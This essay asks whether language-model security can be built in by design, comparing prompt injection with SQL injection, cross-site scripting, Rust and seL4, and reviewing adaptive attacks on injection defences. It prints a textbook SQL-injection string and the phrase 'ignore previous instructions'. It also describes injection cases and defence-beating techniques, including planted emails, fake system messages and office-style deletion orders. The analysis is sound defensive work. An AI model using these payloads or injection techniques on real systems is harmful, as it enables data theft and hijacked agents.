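# Whether language model security can move from patching to construction

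## What is the difference between patching and security by construction?

A large language model is a program that takes text and computes a likely continuation. Developers train it on a vast amount of writing, then train it further to answer questions, follow instructions and refuse certain requests. Companies now connect these models to mailboxes, browsers, databases and payment systems, so a model's output can move money or disclose a document. Language model security is the work of preventing outsiders, and sometimes users, from using these systems for purposes their owners did not intend.

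Patching means fixing or blocking individual flaws or attacks after someone finds them, for instance by filtering out a known malicious phrase or training the model further on an attack that got through. Security by construction means designing the system so that a whole class of flaw cannot occur, as long as certain stated assumptions hold. Database programmers already do this with parameterised queries, which keep a user's input from running as a command. Whether language models allow anything comparable depends a good deal on how they take in text.

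### One sequence of tokens

Software splits a language model's instructions and documents into tokens, which are words or fragments of words, and passes them to the model as a single sequence. In a typical product, the sequence starts with a system message, where the developer sets out the model's job and its limits. The user's request comes next, followed by any web pages, files or emails the application has fetched. OpenAI has published the format that its open-weight gpt-oss models use, called harmony. In its worked example, one string contains a system message, a developer's instruction to answer in riddles, the definitions of two tools and a user's question about the weather in San Francisco. Special marker tokens show where each message starts and who it is from.

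Developers train models to give text more or less authority according to its marker. A system message should take priority over a user's message, and a retrieved web page should be used as information, not followed as instructions. But a marker is only another token in the sequence, and nothing in the model's design forces later computation to follow it. NIST (2025), a taxonomy of attacks on machine learning from the US National Institute of Standards and Technology, attributes many of the security holes in language model applications to this lack of separate channels for data and instructions. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, David C's December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, says that the model has no internal distinction between data and instructions and only predicts the next token.

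Researchers can measure how weak the markers are. In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) wrapped identical passages of ordinary web text in the markers for five roles (system, user, tool output, the model's answer and its private reasoning). They then trained a simple classifier to tell from the model's internal activations which marker surrounded a passage. Because the passages were identical, the classifier could learn only the marker's effect on the activations. They ran it on a short conversation about gardening. With the correct markers, the model's reasoning text scored an average of 85% for "this is my own reasoning". With all markers removed, it scored 83%. When they wrapped the whole conversation in the user's markers, the reasoning text still scored 85%, and only 2% for "user". The text's style affected the classification more than its marker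 did. The case study covers one conversation in one small model, though Ye and colleagues found a similar pattern for text in a user's style across several others.

### From text to action

On its own, a model only emits tokens. Ordinary software makes it an agent by running it in a loop and carrying out its requests. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025), a study from Microsoft, describes this loop. The application sends the model the conversation so far, along with a description of each available tool and its parameters. The model returns either an answer in prose or a tool call, a structured request that names a tool and fills in its arguments. The application parses the request, runs the tool and appends the result to the conversation. It then turns the whole conversation into one string again and sends it to the model, repeating the process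 until the model produces a final answer.

Suppose a user asks a mail assistant to summarise the day's messages. On the first pass, the model outputs a request to read the inbox, and the application fetches the messages and adds them word for word to the model's input. From the second pass on, everything the model produces depends partly on text that strangers wrote. If the model also has a tool for sending mail, that text can influence what it sends.

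The model in this loop never executes anything. As Costa and colleagues point out, the application is responsible for running or declining each tool call the model requests, and a programmer can put a fixed rule at that point that does not depend on the model's judgement.

### Prompt injection and jailbreaks

Prompt injection is text that the model should treat as data but follows as an instruction. It is indirect when the text arrives in content that the agent reads. OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025), a post about the company's browser agent, describes a hypothetical attacker who emails the user a message telling the agent to forward tax documents to an outside address. When the user asks for a summary of unread mail, the agent forwards the documents. In a demonstration that OpenAI ran, a planted email told the agent to send the user's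 chief executive a resignation letter. When the user later asked for an out-of-office reply, the agent came across the email while working on the request and sent the letter.

In direct prompt injection, the user is the attacker. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) describes a hypothetical customer who asks a car dealer's chatbot for a quote and slips in an instruction to grant a large discount.

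A jailbreak is an input that gets a model to produce something its developer trained it to refuse. For example, a model might refuse to explain how to make a drug, but give the instructions once the user asks it to play a character who has no rules and answers every question.

Usage of these terms is not settled. NIST groups jailbreaks and direct injection as "direct prompting attacks", while Beurer-Kellner and colleagues do not distinguish between direct and indirect injection. The categories also overlap, since an attacker can hide a jailbreak in a web page. The terms are still worth separating because the harms take different forms. With indirect injection, the user is often the victim, and in an agent with tools the damage is an action, such as making a payment, deleting a file or leaking a record. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty,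 Kore and colleagues, 2026) calls this a failure of authorisation rather than content. With a jailbreak, the user is the attacker and the harm usually lies in the text itself. A rule at the tool boundary can stop a payment without evaluating the model's text, but it is much less useful when the text is the harm.

### Classes of flaw, one at a time or all at once

A vulnerability class is a set of flaws with one shared cause. Security teams catalogue flaws and classes separately, using a CVE number for a particular flaw in a particular product and a CWE number for the kind of weakness behind it. In their 2024 alert *Malicious Cyber Actors Use SQL Injection Vulnerabilities to Compromise Systems*, the US cybersecurity agency CISA and the FBI asked software makers to record both, and to eliminate entire classes instead of handling flaws case by case.

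Prompt injection attacks all work because the system reads data as commands. They can vary endlessly in wording, language, format and hiding place. David C warns against filters that block phrases such as "ignore previous instructions" because an attacker can always rephrase. Such a filter blocks one attack, but the system still reads data as commands.

Patching can be far more thorough than blocking a list of phrases. For the browser agent in Atlas, OpenAI used reinforcement learning (training by trial and reward) to train a second model to find prompt injections. This attacker proposes a malicious text, a simulator shows how the agent would respond, and the attacker uses the full record of the agent's reasoning and actions to revise its attempt. When an attack works, OpenAI trains a new version of the agent against it and adjusts the surrounding safeguards. This gives the company a head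 start over outsiders, who cannot see the agent's reasoning. But OpenAI writes that the nature of prompt injection makes deterministic guarantees "challenging" and that the problem is unlikely ever to be fully solved. Each round produces an agent that better resists the attacks found so far, and probably some similar ones.

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues make a case for security by construction. They doubt that general-purpose agents can offer reliable guarantees while they rely on the current kind of language model, but they think a whole system may stay secure even when the model inside it is vulnerable. Their principle is that once an agent has taken in untrusted input, it must be impossible for that input to trigger any consequential action. Calling an action impossible means little until someone specifies what the attacker can do.

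### The threat model

A threat model specifies what the attacker can control, see and know. *On Evaluating Adversarial Robustness* (2019) treats it as part of the defence, because it defines the conditions under which the defence should hold and what the defence guarantees. Without a threat model, a claim of security is either impossible to refute, because any failure can be dismissed as out of scope, or trivial to refute, because an attacker with unlimited powers can always win.

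Costa and colleagues give a worked example for agents in which they trust the user's messages, the model, the system message and the tool descriptions. The attacker can tamper with data that tools fetch from untrusted sources, such as the public web, and can observe the effects of some tool calls, but does not see the model's inputs and outputs directly. Narisetty and colleagues describe a similar attacker who also knows the system's design, including its defences, and can keep adapting the attack to them. This attacker cannot alter the model's weights (the numbers that training produces) or the software that enforces the rules.

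Such statements are deliberately narrow. An agent can misread an honest request and send the wrong file even with no attacker involved, and a defence against injection does not guarantee that this won't happen. Results also do not carry over from one threat model to another. *Physical AI* (2026), a survey of AI systems that act in the physical world, points out that success rates for attacks with different goals measure different risks, so they cannot be compared directly.

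### Closed, narrowed or open

A class of attack is closed by construction if no input the attacker can supply under the threat model makes the system cause the harm, whatever the language model inside it does. The designer therefore has to assume that a model which has read the attacker's text may output whatever the attacker wants. NIST similarly suggests designing applications on the assumption that the model can and will produce malicious output if malicious people can reach it.

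A class is narrowed if the design bounds the harm but doesn't rule it out, and open if the design sets no bound. For example, suppose the mail assistant's attacker can only send the user email, and the harm is that the user's private mail reaches the attacker.

| Design of the assistant | Worst case if the model obeys the attacker | Verdict for this harm |
|---|---|---|
| Reads the whole mailbox and sends mail to any address | The attacker receives everything | Open |
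| Reads only today's messages and sends mail to any address | The attacker receives one day's mail | Narrowed |
| Reads the whole mailbox, has no tool that sends anything, and shows its summary as plain text | The attacker receives nothing | Closed |

Security has to be judged separately for each harm. Under the last design, an email containing injected instructions can still distort the summary, and nothing limits by how much, so the assistant is vulnerable to producing misleading text. It also can no longer send mail, a feature some users will have wanted.

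A measured attack success rate is a different kind of evidence, because it counts how often a finite list of attacks succeeds against one model. AgentDojo, a standard benchmark for agents, has 629 security cases. If an agent withstood all of them, and if the cases were independent random draws from some larger population of attacks (a generous assumption), we could say with 95% confidence that the success rate in that population is below about 0.5%. But attackers search for an input that works rather than drawing at random, and they need only one. Even a low fixed rate adds up over repeated attempts. If each malicious email independently has a 1% chance of success, a hundred emails give the attacker a 63% chance of succeeding at least once. Narisetty and colleagues argue that the field has mistaken resistance to a known set of attacks for resistance to attackers, a mistake that came to light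 when researchers tailored their attacks to the defences.

Rates are still useful. They are often the only evidence for an open class, and a company may reasonably prefer an agent that does a wide range of work and rarely fails to one that provably cannot leak mail but also cannot send it.

Calling something "closed" is justified only if certain parts of the system work correctly. Those parts are, in practice, its trusted computing base. NIST's glossary entry *trusted computing base (TCB)* defines the term as the totality of protection mechanisms, in hardware, firmware and software, that together enforce a security policy. Under patching, the model belongs to this base, because security depends on how it responds to text nobody has tested. Construction tries to move the security decision out of the model and into a smaller amount of ordinary code. For the mail assistant without a sending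 tool, that code includes the program that runs the loop, the tool that reads mail, the software that displays the summary and the operating system underneath.

Any of these can break the promise. If the screen loads images from web addresses in the summary, the model can write an address that contains private text, and loading the image sends that text to whoever runs the server. NIST lists image rendering as a known way to exfiltrate private data, meaning to send it to someone not entitled to it. The table's last row therefore depends on the program actually showing the summary as plain text.

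Correct code is not enough either, because enforcement also depends on people entering the right parameters for the policy, according to the glossary entry *trusted computing base (TCB)* from ATIS, a US telecommunications standards body. For agents, the parameter that is easiest to get wrong is often the record of where each piece of text came from. Narisetty and colleagues regard assigning those origins as the trusted base of every defence that relies on labels, and find it under-specified in all the systems they surveyed. Most designs trust whatever the user types, and the software can't distinguish typed text from a paragraph the user pasted from an attacker's web page.

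## How did software engineers remove whole classes of vulnerability?

Long before language models, programs built commands by joining strings, some of which came from strangers. Engineers have largely dealt with a few of the resulting flaws by changing how people write programs. Database queries are the simplest case.

### SQL injection

Most websites keep their records in a database and query it in a language called SQL. Suppose a bank's website looks up a balance by joining a fixed piece of SQL to whatever name the visitor types. For a visitor named tom, the finished query is:

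```
SELECT account_balance FROM user_data WHERE user_name = 'tom'
```

An attacker types `tom' or '1'='1` instead, a string that appears in OWASP's *SQL Injection Prevention Cheat Sheet*, a guide from a non-profit that works on web security. The quotation mark after "tom" ends the name early, and the rest of the input becomes part of the command:

```
SELECT account_balance FROM user_data WHERE user_name = 'tom' or '1'='1'
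```

Because `'1'='1'` is always true, the condition holds for every row, and the database returns every customer's balance.

Programmers can try to escape the input, which means marking each quotation mark so that the database reads it as an ordinary character. OWASP strongly discourages relying on this, because the rules differ from one database to another and escaping can't guarantee to stop every injection. With a parameterised query, the programmer writes the command in advance and leaves a placeholder for the name:

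```
SELECT account_balance FROM user_data WHERE user_name = ?
```

The database's parser analyses this query according to SQL's grammar and fixes its structure as a comparison between a column and a single value. The program supplies the name separately, and the database never parses it as SQL. If the attacker sends the same string as before, the database looks for a customer whose name is literally `tom' or '1'='1` and finds nobody.

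This works because SQL is a formal language. Its grammar defines where a value starts and ends, so a designer can reserve a slot that holds only a value. Narisetty and colleagues sum up the history of these flaws as "detection lost and structure won", and point out that natural language has no such grammar.

The slot can't hold the name of a table or column, or the direction of a sort, so a program that lets users choose these should pick from a fixed list. Parameterised queries prevent injection in programs that use them throughout, but they don't check whether the user is entitled to the answer. If someone changes the account number in a request from their own to a neighbour's, the new number is still a valid value, and the query runs as written. OWASP therefore recommends restricting what each application's database account can read or change.

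### Cross-site scripting

In cross-site scripting, the attacker's text becomes part of a web page instead of a database query. Web pages are written in HTML, which mixes text with markup, and the markup can include scripts, which are small programs that the browser runs. Kern's *Securing the Tangled Web* (2014), an account of Google's work on the problem, gives the example of a hypothetical photo-sharing site that notifies users when someone shares an album with them. The site inserts the album's title into the notification's HTML. If a malicious user puts a script in the title, the recipient's browser runs it, and the script can do anything on the site that the recipient can.

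The basic remedy is output encoding. Before inserting text into a page, the program replaces characters that have a special meaning in HTML with codes that the browser displays as ordinary characters. For example, `<` becomes `&lt;`, so a script hidden in the text appears on the page instead of running. But the right treatment depends on where the text goes. A web address that starts with `javascript:` makes the browser run the rest of the address as a program, and it may contain no characters that HTML encoding would change. When text is used as a web address, the program therefore has to check that it starts with something harmless, such as `https`.

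In a large application, data can reach a page by thousands of routes. To rule out the flaw, a reviewer would have to trace each one back to its source, often through a database and several programs. Kern writes that training, code review and testing caught many of these bugs at Google, perhaps most, but never made its security team very confident that none were left.

Google's engineers changed the default so that the software that fills in page templates encodes every string to suit its position, wherever the string came from. Programmers cannot switch this off. When a page needs to include markup from users, such as a profile with coloured text and links, the program has to supply a value of a special type, `SafeHtml`. Application code cannot make this value directly from a string and has to use one of a small set of reviewed functions, such as a sanitiser, which strips out any markup that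 could run a script. A checking tool rejects code that tries to write plain strings into a page by another route. Reviewers can then concentrate on the sanitiser, the template system and a few similar components.

One of Google's largest applications, with more than 1,000 templates, had 31 cross-site scripting bugs in 2012 and switched to the new system in early 2013. In the year to mid-2014 it had four, all in the first six months. A second application, still partway through the switch, went from 21 bugs to nine. Kern calls these figures anecdotal because the code and the developers' training also changed over the same period.

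Later work enforced the rules more strictly. *If It's Not Secure, It Should Not Compile* (Bangert, 2021) describes how Google built them into its compilers, which translate source code into a form ready to run, so that a program that breaks the rules does not compile. W3C's *Trusted Types* (2024), a web standard, moves the check into the browser, where more than 60 functions can turn text into running code. On a site that turns on Trusted Types, these functions reject plain strings and accept only typed values created by policies that the site's developers write and review.

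According to the web security company PortSwigger, Google has applied Trusted Types to more than 130 services. PortSwigger also quotes a researcher who warns that a Trusted Types policy may contain a mistake or rely on a sanitiser that an attacker can bypass.

### Memory safety

C and C++, the languages behind most operating systems and browsers, let a program read and write memory by address and rely on the programmer to ensure the address is valid. In a buffer overflow, a program writes past the end of the block of memory it set aside. In a use-after-free, it keeps using a block it has already released. An attacker who controls the data involved can overwrite other data the program relies on, sometimes including the address of the instructions it will run next.

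Rust, a newer language for the same kind of work, has a compiler that checks for these errors before the program runs. Each value has exactly one owner, and the program frees the value's memory when the owner goes out of scope. Other code can borrow the value through a reference, but no reference may outlast the value. At any moment, a value may have either any number of read-only references or a single reference that can change it.

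Suppose a program keeps a reference to the first item in a list and then adds an item at the end. If the list has outgrown its block of memory, the program copies it to a larger block and frees the old one. The reference now points to freed memory. A C++ compiler will normally accept this program. Rust's compiler rejects it if the program uses the reference afterwards, because adding an item requires sole access to the list. Rust's compiler cannot always predict which position in a list a program will access, so it also inserts checks that halt the program if the position is out of range.

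Google began moving new development on Android, its mobile operating system, to memory-safe languages around 2019. In 2019, memory-safety flaws made up 76% of Android's vulnerabilities. Google reported that the share had fallen to 24% by 2024, and Vander Stoep (2025) reported in *Rust in Android* that it fell below 20% for the first time in 2025. The number of memory-safety flaws also fell over the period, apart from a slight rise in 2023, to a projected 36 in 2024, so the share did not fall only because other flaws became more common.

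Google did this without rewriting the old code, and most of Android was still in unsafe languages in 2024. People keep finding and fixing flaws, so code that nobody otherwise changes gradually gets safer. If flaws last an average of λ years and their lifetimes follow an exponential distribution, the fraction left after t years is e^(−t/λ). Google used an average of 2.5 years in a simulation based on projects like Android. At that average, e^(−2), or about 14%, of flaws remain after five years, so five-year-old code has roughly 7.4 times fewer flaws per line than new code. With the longer lifetimes from a 2022 academic study of open-source software, the ratio is 3.4.

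Most flaws are therefore in recent code, and if a team stops adding new flaws, the number of old ones can fall over time. In the simulation, memory-safety flaws fell sharply even though the amount of unsafe code kept growing. Android did somewhat better than the simulation, possibly because Google was also making its C and C++ code safer, so Rust may not explain all of the improvement.

Vander Stoep also reports that Android had about 5 million lines of Rust with one known potential memory-safety vulnerability, or 0.2 per million lines, compared with a historical rate of around 1,000 per million for its C and C++. One case is little evidence, and people have had less time to look for flaws in the Rust code. Still, if such finds are independent random events, the upper end of the 95% confidence interval for Rust is about 1.1 per million lines, roughly 900 times lower than the C and C++ rate.

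Rust didn't slow Android's developers down. They rolled back medium and large Rust changes about a quarter as often as C++ changes, and Rust changes spent about 25% less time in review. These comparisons cover changes of similar size by overlapping groups of developers, but the choice of language wasn't random.

The one potential vulnerability was in CrabbyAVIF, an image-decoding library, in a block of code marked "unsafe". Inside such blocks, the programmer takes over responsibility for some of the checks. An operating system needs them to control hardware and call code in other languages, and they make up about 4% of Android's Rust. Google's engineers caught the bug, a buffer overflow (CVE-2025-48530), before it reached a public release. Most devices also had a second layer of defence. Android's default memory allocator, Scudo, surrounds large blocks of memory with guard pages that no program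 may touch, so the overflow caused a crash instead of silent corruption.

No programming language eliminates logic errors. A Rust program that doesn't check whether a user is allowed to open a file will open it for an unauthorized user without causing a memory error. More than 80% of Android's vulnerabilities in 2025 were unrelated to memory safety.

### A kernel with a proof

A language like Rust rules out certain kinds of mistake. A mathematical proof can show that a program does exactly what its specification requires. The standard example is seL4, a microkernel. A kernel is the part of an operating system that has full control of the hardware, and a microkernel is a pared-down version of it. Any bug in a kernel can do unlimited damage, so the kernel belongs to the trusted computing base of everything that runs on it. seL4's designers kept it to 8,700 lines of C and 600 of assembly, and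 moved services such as device drivers into ordinary programs outside it.

*seL4* (Klein et al., 2010) uses a tiny program to show what a proof adds to testing. If x is less than y, the program divides x by y, and otherwise it divides y by x. Two tests, with x = 4 and y = 2 and then with x = 8 and y = 16, run every line and take both branches. But the program divides by zero when x = 0 and y = −1. Testers would soon find this bug in a program this small, but in a large one they can't be sure they have tried every case that matters.

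The seL4 team wrote an abstract specification of what each kernel operation should do, a more detailed one of how it should do it, and then the C code. They used a proof assistant, which is software that checks each step of a proof, to show that the C code does only what the detailed specification allows, and that the detailed specification allows only what the abstract one allows. Their model lets programs running on the kernel do anything, so the proof also covers malicious programs. If the proof's assumptions hold, seL4 has no buffer overflows and never runs code that an attacker has injected into it.

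The proof took about 20 person-years, including nine for tools and libraries, while designing and writing the kernel took about two and a half. Klein and colleagues estimated that a second kernel would take eight person-years, including the proof. Proving that the C code matched the detailed specification uncovered 160 bugs, of which testing and other checks had found only 16. Later changes took very different amounts of work. The team designed and wrote one new system call in a day and updated the proof in less than a week. Another change affected less than 5% of the code but took about a person-year to re-verify because it violated properties that much of the proof relied on.

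The original proof assumed that the compiler, the assembly code, the hardware and about 1,200 lines of start-up code were correct. The seL4 project has since reduced these assumptions by extending its proofs down to the binary code that the processor runs. It says the remaining assumptions are much more likely to cause trouble than the proofs. Klein and colleagues also stress that a correct kernel is not secure for every purpose. Their proof does not rule out covert channels, in which one program signals to another through a side effect such as timing, and the programs running on the kernel can still have bugs.

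### Conditions of success

These four cases have a good deal in common.

| Case | Formal boundary | Safe default | What enforces it | What still has to be right |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Parameterised queries | Command and value in SQL's grammar | Input is only ever a value | The database, for queries that use placeholders | The database software, and any query still built from strings |
| Typed HTML | Text and markup at each position in a page | Encode every string | Build tools and the browser | Templates, sanitisers and policies |
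| Rust | Valid and invalid uses of memory | Checks apply unless a block is marked unsafe | The compiler and run-time checks | The compiler, unsafe blocks and any C or C++ they call |
| seL4 | Behaviour the specification allows | No access to an object without an explicit token | The kernel, with a machine-checked proof of its code | Hardware, start-up code and the specification |

The boundary has to be precise enough for a machine to check without judging what anyone meant. For example, a compiler can check whether a reference outlasts its value, and a browser can distinguish a string from a typed value.

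The default also has to suit most legitimate uses, or people will keep asking for exceptions. Google could encode every string because most of what a web page displays is plain text and ordinary addresses, which encoding does not break. Pages that needed user-supplied markup were rare, so the engineers could review each exception.

Enforcement was the weakest part of the defence against SQL injection. Parameterised queries work in every program that uses them, but a typical database will also run a query that a careless programmer has built from strings. CISA and the FBI were still warning about SQL injection in 2024, long after the remedy was well known. Kern found that even in medium-sized projects, programmers end up breaking coding rules unless a tool checks for violations.

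Each design also leaves a small part that people have to get right, such as a sanitiser or an unsafe block. Experts can give that part far more attention than they could give a whole application. The remaining failures of construction tend to occur there, as in CrabbyAVIF.

### Finding and fixing bugs with AI

Before turning to memory-safe languages, the industry tried patching, then mitigations that made flaws harder to exploit, then automated bug-hunting tools such as fuzzers, which run a program on huge numbers of generated inputs. Google concluded in 2024 that all of these had helped but none had reduced the risk from memory-safety flaws to an acceptable level. Even heavily fuzzed code still contained vulnerabilities. AI systems have since become much better at finding bugs, so this conclusion needs to be reassessed.

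Anthropic's *Project Glasswing* (2026) reports that the AI company and about 50 partners used a model called Claude Mythos Preview to search important software for vulnerabilities. In roughly a month they found more than 10,000 of high or critical severity. Mozilla found and fixed 271 vulnerabilities in version 150 of its Firefox browser, over ten times as many as it had found in version 148 with an earlier model. Anthropic also scanned more than 1,000 open-source projects. Human reviewers, mostly from outside security firms, checked 1,752 findings the model had rated high or critical. They confirmed 90.6% as real vulnerabilities and 62.4% as high or critical.

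Fixing vulnerabilities has been much slower than finding them. By May, projects had patched 75 of the 530 serious flaws that Anthropic had reported to them, and some maintainers had asked the company to slow down. By 2 November, Anthropic's public dashboard (2026) listed 5,087 disclosed vulnerabilities across 680 projects and 629 known patches, about one for every eight vulnerabilities.

*After 7-months, Glasswing Overwelms Maintainers with Underwhelming Findings* (2026), by the security firm VulnCheck, is harsher. It compares 37,966 findings with only 217 that Anthropic's ledger marks as fixed. That comparison is too pessimistic, because maintainers can't fix flaws nobody has reported to them, and the ledger seems incomplete, since VulnCheck traced 442 published vulnerabilities to Anthropic. VulnCheck's evidence on the quality of the reports is more troubling. The maintainers of curl, a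 widely used tool for transferring data, rejected 19 of 34 reports from an Anthropic service that passes findings on without human review. They confirmed six as low-severity flaws and had yet to assess the other nine. Checking findings carefully before reporting them helps, but it leaves far fewer reports. Wolf and Cochran (2026), in *Maintainers don't need more AI bug reports. They need fixes*, describe a pilot in which GitHub and Microsoft turned thousands of raw AI findings into 99 checked reports for six projects.

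Organisations that control their own code can patch it faster. Within three weeks of Anthropic launching a security tool for businesses, customers had used Claude Opus 4.7 to patch over 2,100 vulnerabilities.

Researchers disagree about how well AI writes the patches. In *Frontier Models' Vulnerability Patches are Often F.L.A.W.E.D*, Mierczuk, Michaels and Hoodlet asked two leading models of mid-2026 to fix six complex vulnerabilities under a range of conditions. Wheeler's *Finding and Fixing Vulnerabilities Using AI* compares their results with a later critique. In the original study, 26.0% of attempts fully fixed the flaw without materially changing how the program behaved, while 53.9% left the flaw in place, added a new one, or both. According to the critique, some prompts had told the models to apply the wrong fix or forbidden them to run tests, and 86% of 3,067 patches blocked the exploit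 supplied with the task.

Both figures can be right, because a patch may block one exploit but leave other routes to the same flaw. Mierczuk and colleagues often saw models add a check that satisfied the tests but didn't address the root cause. Pogorelec (2026) similarly reports in *AI vulnerability patching has a grading problem* that AI tools can stop a crash without fixing the bug behind it, and that benchmark scores often don't reflect the difference. The original study left out simple flaws, so these findings don't show that models do badly on them.

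Meanwhile, defenders have less time to fix flaws. Anthropic's *Updating our coordinated vulnerability disclosure policy timelines* (2026) cuts the period before publication from 90 days to 30 for high- and critical-severity flaws, and to 45 for the rest, for vulnerabilities reported from January 2027. Anthropic reasons that if one model can find a bug, another is increasingly likely to find it too, so the company can no longer expect a flaw to stay private for months.

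On balance, this evidence strengthens the case for both approaches, but patching benefits most in the short term. A given version of a program contains a finite number of flaws, and developers can now find many more of them before release. AI can also look for the logic errors that memory-safe languages don't prevent. Claude Mythos Preview found one such error in wolfSSL, a cryptography library used on billions of devices. The flaw involved no memory error, but it would have let an attacker forge the certificates that identify websites.

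The case for construction also grows stronger, because checking and fixing flaws and deploying patches are now the bottleneck, and none of that work is needed for a flaw that cannot occur. Patching and construction also work well together, since an AI system can search a sanitiser or a few unsafe blocks far more thoroughly than a whole operating system. But Android's policy of leaving old code alone may need revisiting. The curve behind that policy is based on flaws people found with earlier tools, and AI may find many more in old code than the curve predicts. If so, rewriting or isolating that code would be worth more than Google assumed in 2024, and models that can write Rust should make the rewriting cheaper.

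All of this evidence comes from ordinary code, where a developer can permanently remove a flaw by correcting particular lines. Developers can't trace a successful prompt injection to a faulty line in the model and correct it.

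## Why has repairing the model not closed a class of attack?

Developers can still change how a model responds to hostile text, either by training it further or by controlling what reaches it. The simplest repair is a filter, a separate program that reads text before it reaches the model and blocks anything that looks like an attack. Most filters are small language models trained on examples of harmless text and known attacks. Some also read the model's output and block answers that look harmful.

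Other defences add cues to the input. Spotlighting marks retrieved text to show where it came from. Prompt sandwiching repeats the user's request after the retrieved text, so the request is the last thing the model reads.

Developers can change the model itself through adversarial training, in which they show it many attacks and train it to carry on with the user's task or, for jailbreaks, to refuse. They can also train it to rank instructions by source. OpenAI's version, the instruction hierarchy, trains the model on conflicting instructions to obey the source with the most authority. Existing attacks can still override this training. Narisetty and colleagues cite tests of the instruction hierarchy on GPT-4o-mini, a small OpenAI model, in which such attacks succeeded 68% of the time on one benchmark and 75% on another.

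*Defending against Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks via Reasoning-enabled Task Alignment* (He, Wang and colleagues, 2026) attributes the failures of such defences to their reliance on features of the untrusted text, such as its wording, its position between markers or its effect on a trial run of the agent. None of them checks whether the agent's next action follows from the user's request. The attacker writes the text and can therefore change these features while keeping the same goal. For example, an automated search got past a filter trained on commands by rewriting an order to forward an earnings report as a remark about what the team had agreed that morning. Against a model trained to ignore injected commands, the search found a first-person account of work already under way, with the malicious step as the natural next one.

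### Twelve defences under adaptive attack

*The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) is the most thorough test of these repairs. The team, which included researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, attacked twelve recent defences with methods that could adapt to each one. Most of these defences had attack success rates near zero in their original evaluations.

All their attacks follow the same loop. The attacker proposes some candidate texts, scores how well each one works on the defended system, selects the most promising and uses them to write the next batch. Nasr and colleagues ran this loop in four ways:

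- **Gradients.** The attacker uses the model's internal numbers to work out which tokens to swap. The team found this unreliable and tried it on only one defence.
- **Reinforcement learning.** An attacking model makes five attempts per session and sees the system's reply and a score after each. Training then updates the attacking model, using 32 sessions for each test case.
- **Search.** A language model rewrites earlier attempts, while an evolutionary algorithm keeps a varied pool of the best ones.
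- **People.** More than 500 contestants competed for $20,000 in prizes. They wrote text for the agent to find in a tool's results, watched its reasoning and tool calls, and tried again.

The automated attacks had these results:

| Defence | How it works | Attack success rate |
|---|---|---|
| Spotlighting | Marks where text came from | Above 95% (search) |
| Prompt sandwiching | Repeats the user's request after untrusted text | Above 95% (search) |
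| RPO | Adds a prompt optimised to block jailbreaks | 98% (reinforcement learning), 96% (gradients) |
| Circuit Breakers | Trains the model against jailbreaks | 100% (reinforcement learning) |
| StruQ | Trains the model to obey only a marked instruction | Every case tested (reinforcement learning) |
| MetaSecAlign | Trains the model to prefer answers that ignore injections | 96% (search) |
| Protect AI Detector | Filter | Above 90% (search) |
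| PromptGuard | Filter | Above 90% (search) |
| Model Armor | Filter, sold by Google | Above 90% (search) |
| PIGuard | Filter | 71% (search) |
| Data Sentinel | Checks whether a text stops a second model from repeating a secret key | Every case tested (reinforcement learning) |
| MELON | Reruns the agent without the user's request and compares the tool calls | 76%, or 95% if the attacker knows the design (search) |

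AgentDojo's fixed attacks had succeeded as little as 1% of the time against spotlighting and sandwiching, and the reported rate for MetaSecAlign was 2%. The team followed each defence's original test procedure, so the benchmarks and models differ and the rows should not be read as a ranking. The AgentDojo tests used only 80 cases, but that is easily enough to distinguish 2% from 96%.

Many of the successful texts resembled routine office messages. One told the agent that company policy required it to log each rescheduled meeting by deleting a particular file. A filter strict enough to block that sentence would also block a lot of ordinary business mail. Against prompt sandwiching, which repeats the user's request, the search produced text that presented the malicious steps as prerequisites for that request, so repeating it did not help. Against MELON, which looks for tool calls that recur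 when the agent is only asked to summarise, the search added a note telling any system summarising the file to ignore the instructions above, so the malicious calls appeared only when the agent was carrying out the user's request.

The defences based on training were mostly broken by text that imitated a system message. This fits Ye and colleagues' finding that a passage's style can affect how a model represents it more than its marker does.

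Human contestants beat all 40 challenges. On a selected set of scenarios, the search attack succeeded 69% of the time, while the contestants as a group succeeded every time. This compares hundreds of people with one run of a program, so it doesn't mean that a typical person beats the search. But a defence that survives an automated attack may still fail against people.

These tests favour the attacker. Nasr and colleagues did not tightly limit computing power, and the search attack had access to a filter's confidence score. Someone who plants text on a web page will rarely see how a stranger's agent reacted to it. The researchers defend their choice by citing the usual security standard, which assumes that the attacker knows the design and has ample resources. That assumption is also fairly realistic for widely sold products, since an attacker can buy the same assistant and practise on it.

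He, Wang and colleagues ran a smaller test on two small open models and found a smaller effect. On one model, the best attack on each defence succeeded on average 21.7% of the time with fixed attacks and 41.8% with adaptive ones. On the other, the gap was 11.5 percentage points. Even these gaps may be overstated, because the adaptive attacks ran only on 40 cases already known to be vulnerable.

Jailbreaks show a similar pattern on more recent models. The Italian research institute AI4I (2026) tested Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.8 and Claude Fable 5 in June 2026 and confirmed 1,620 harmful answers from Opus and 702 from Fable. Almost all came from attacks in which another model rewrote the prompt after a refusal, usually succeeding within one or two rewrites. Against Opus 4.8, this kind of adaptive search succeeded 27.6% of the time on one category of request.

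### Training against an attacker that adapts

Research on image classifiers had already shown much the same thing. Training a classifier against a fixed set of altered images gave little protection once attackers looked for new alterations. According to Nasr and colleagues, only training that searches for new attacks as it goes has produced meaningful robustness, and only against the kinds of attack it searches for.

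He, Wang and colleagues apply this idea to agents in a method called RETA. An attacking model earns extra reward for strategies that earlier attacks did not use, which stops it from repeating one trick. The defending model then learns to reason, after each tool result, about whether its next action serves the user's task. Six kinds of adaptive attack each succeeded less than 10% of the time, with average success rates of 2.92% and 3.75% on the two models.

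*AttriGuard* (He, Zhu and colleagues, 2026) leaves the model unchanged and tests its actions. Before allowing a tool call, it runs the agent again with the retrieved text reworded to sound less like a command. If the agent no longer makes the call, the text probably caused it, and AttriGuard blocks the call. With Gemini 2.5, an adaptive attack succeeded 6.6% of the time against AttriGuard, compared with 29.5% to 82.0% against other defences. The paper states that AttriGuard is not provably robust, because the agent still reads the attacker's text while it plans.

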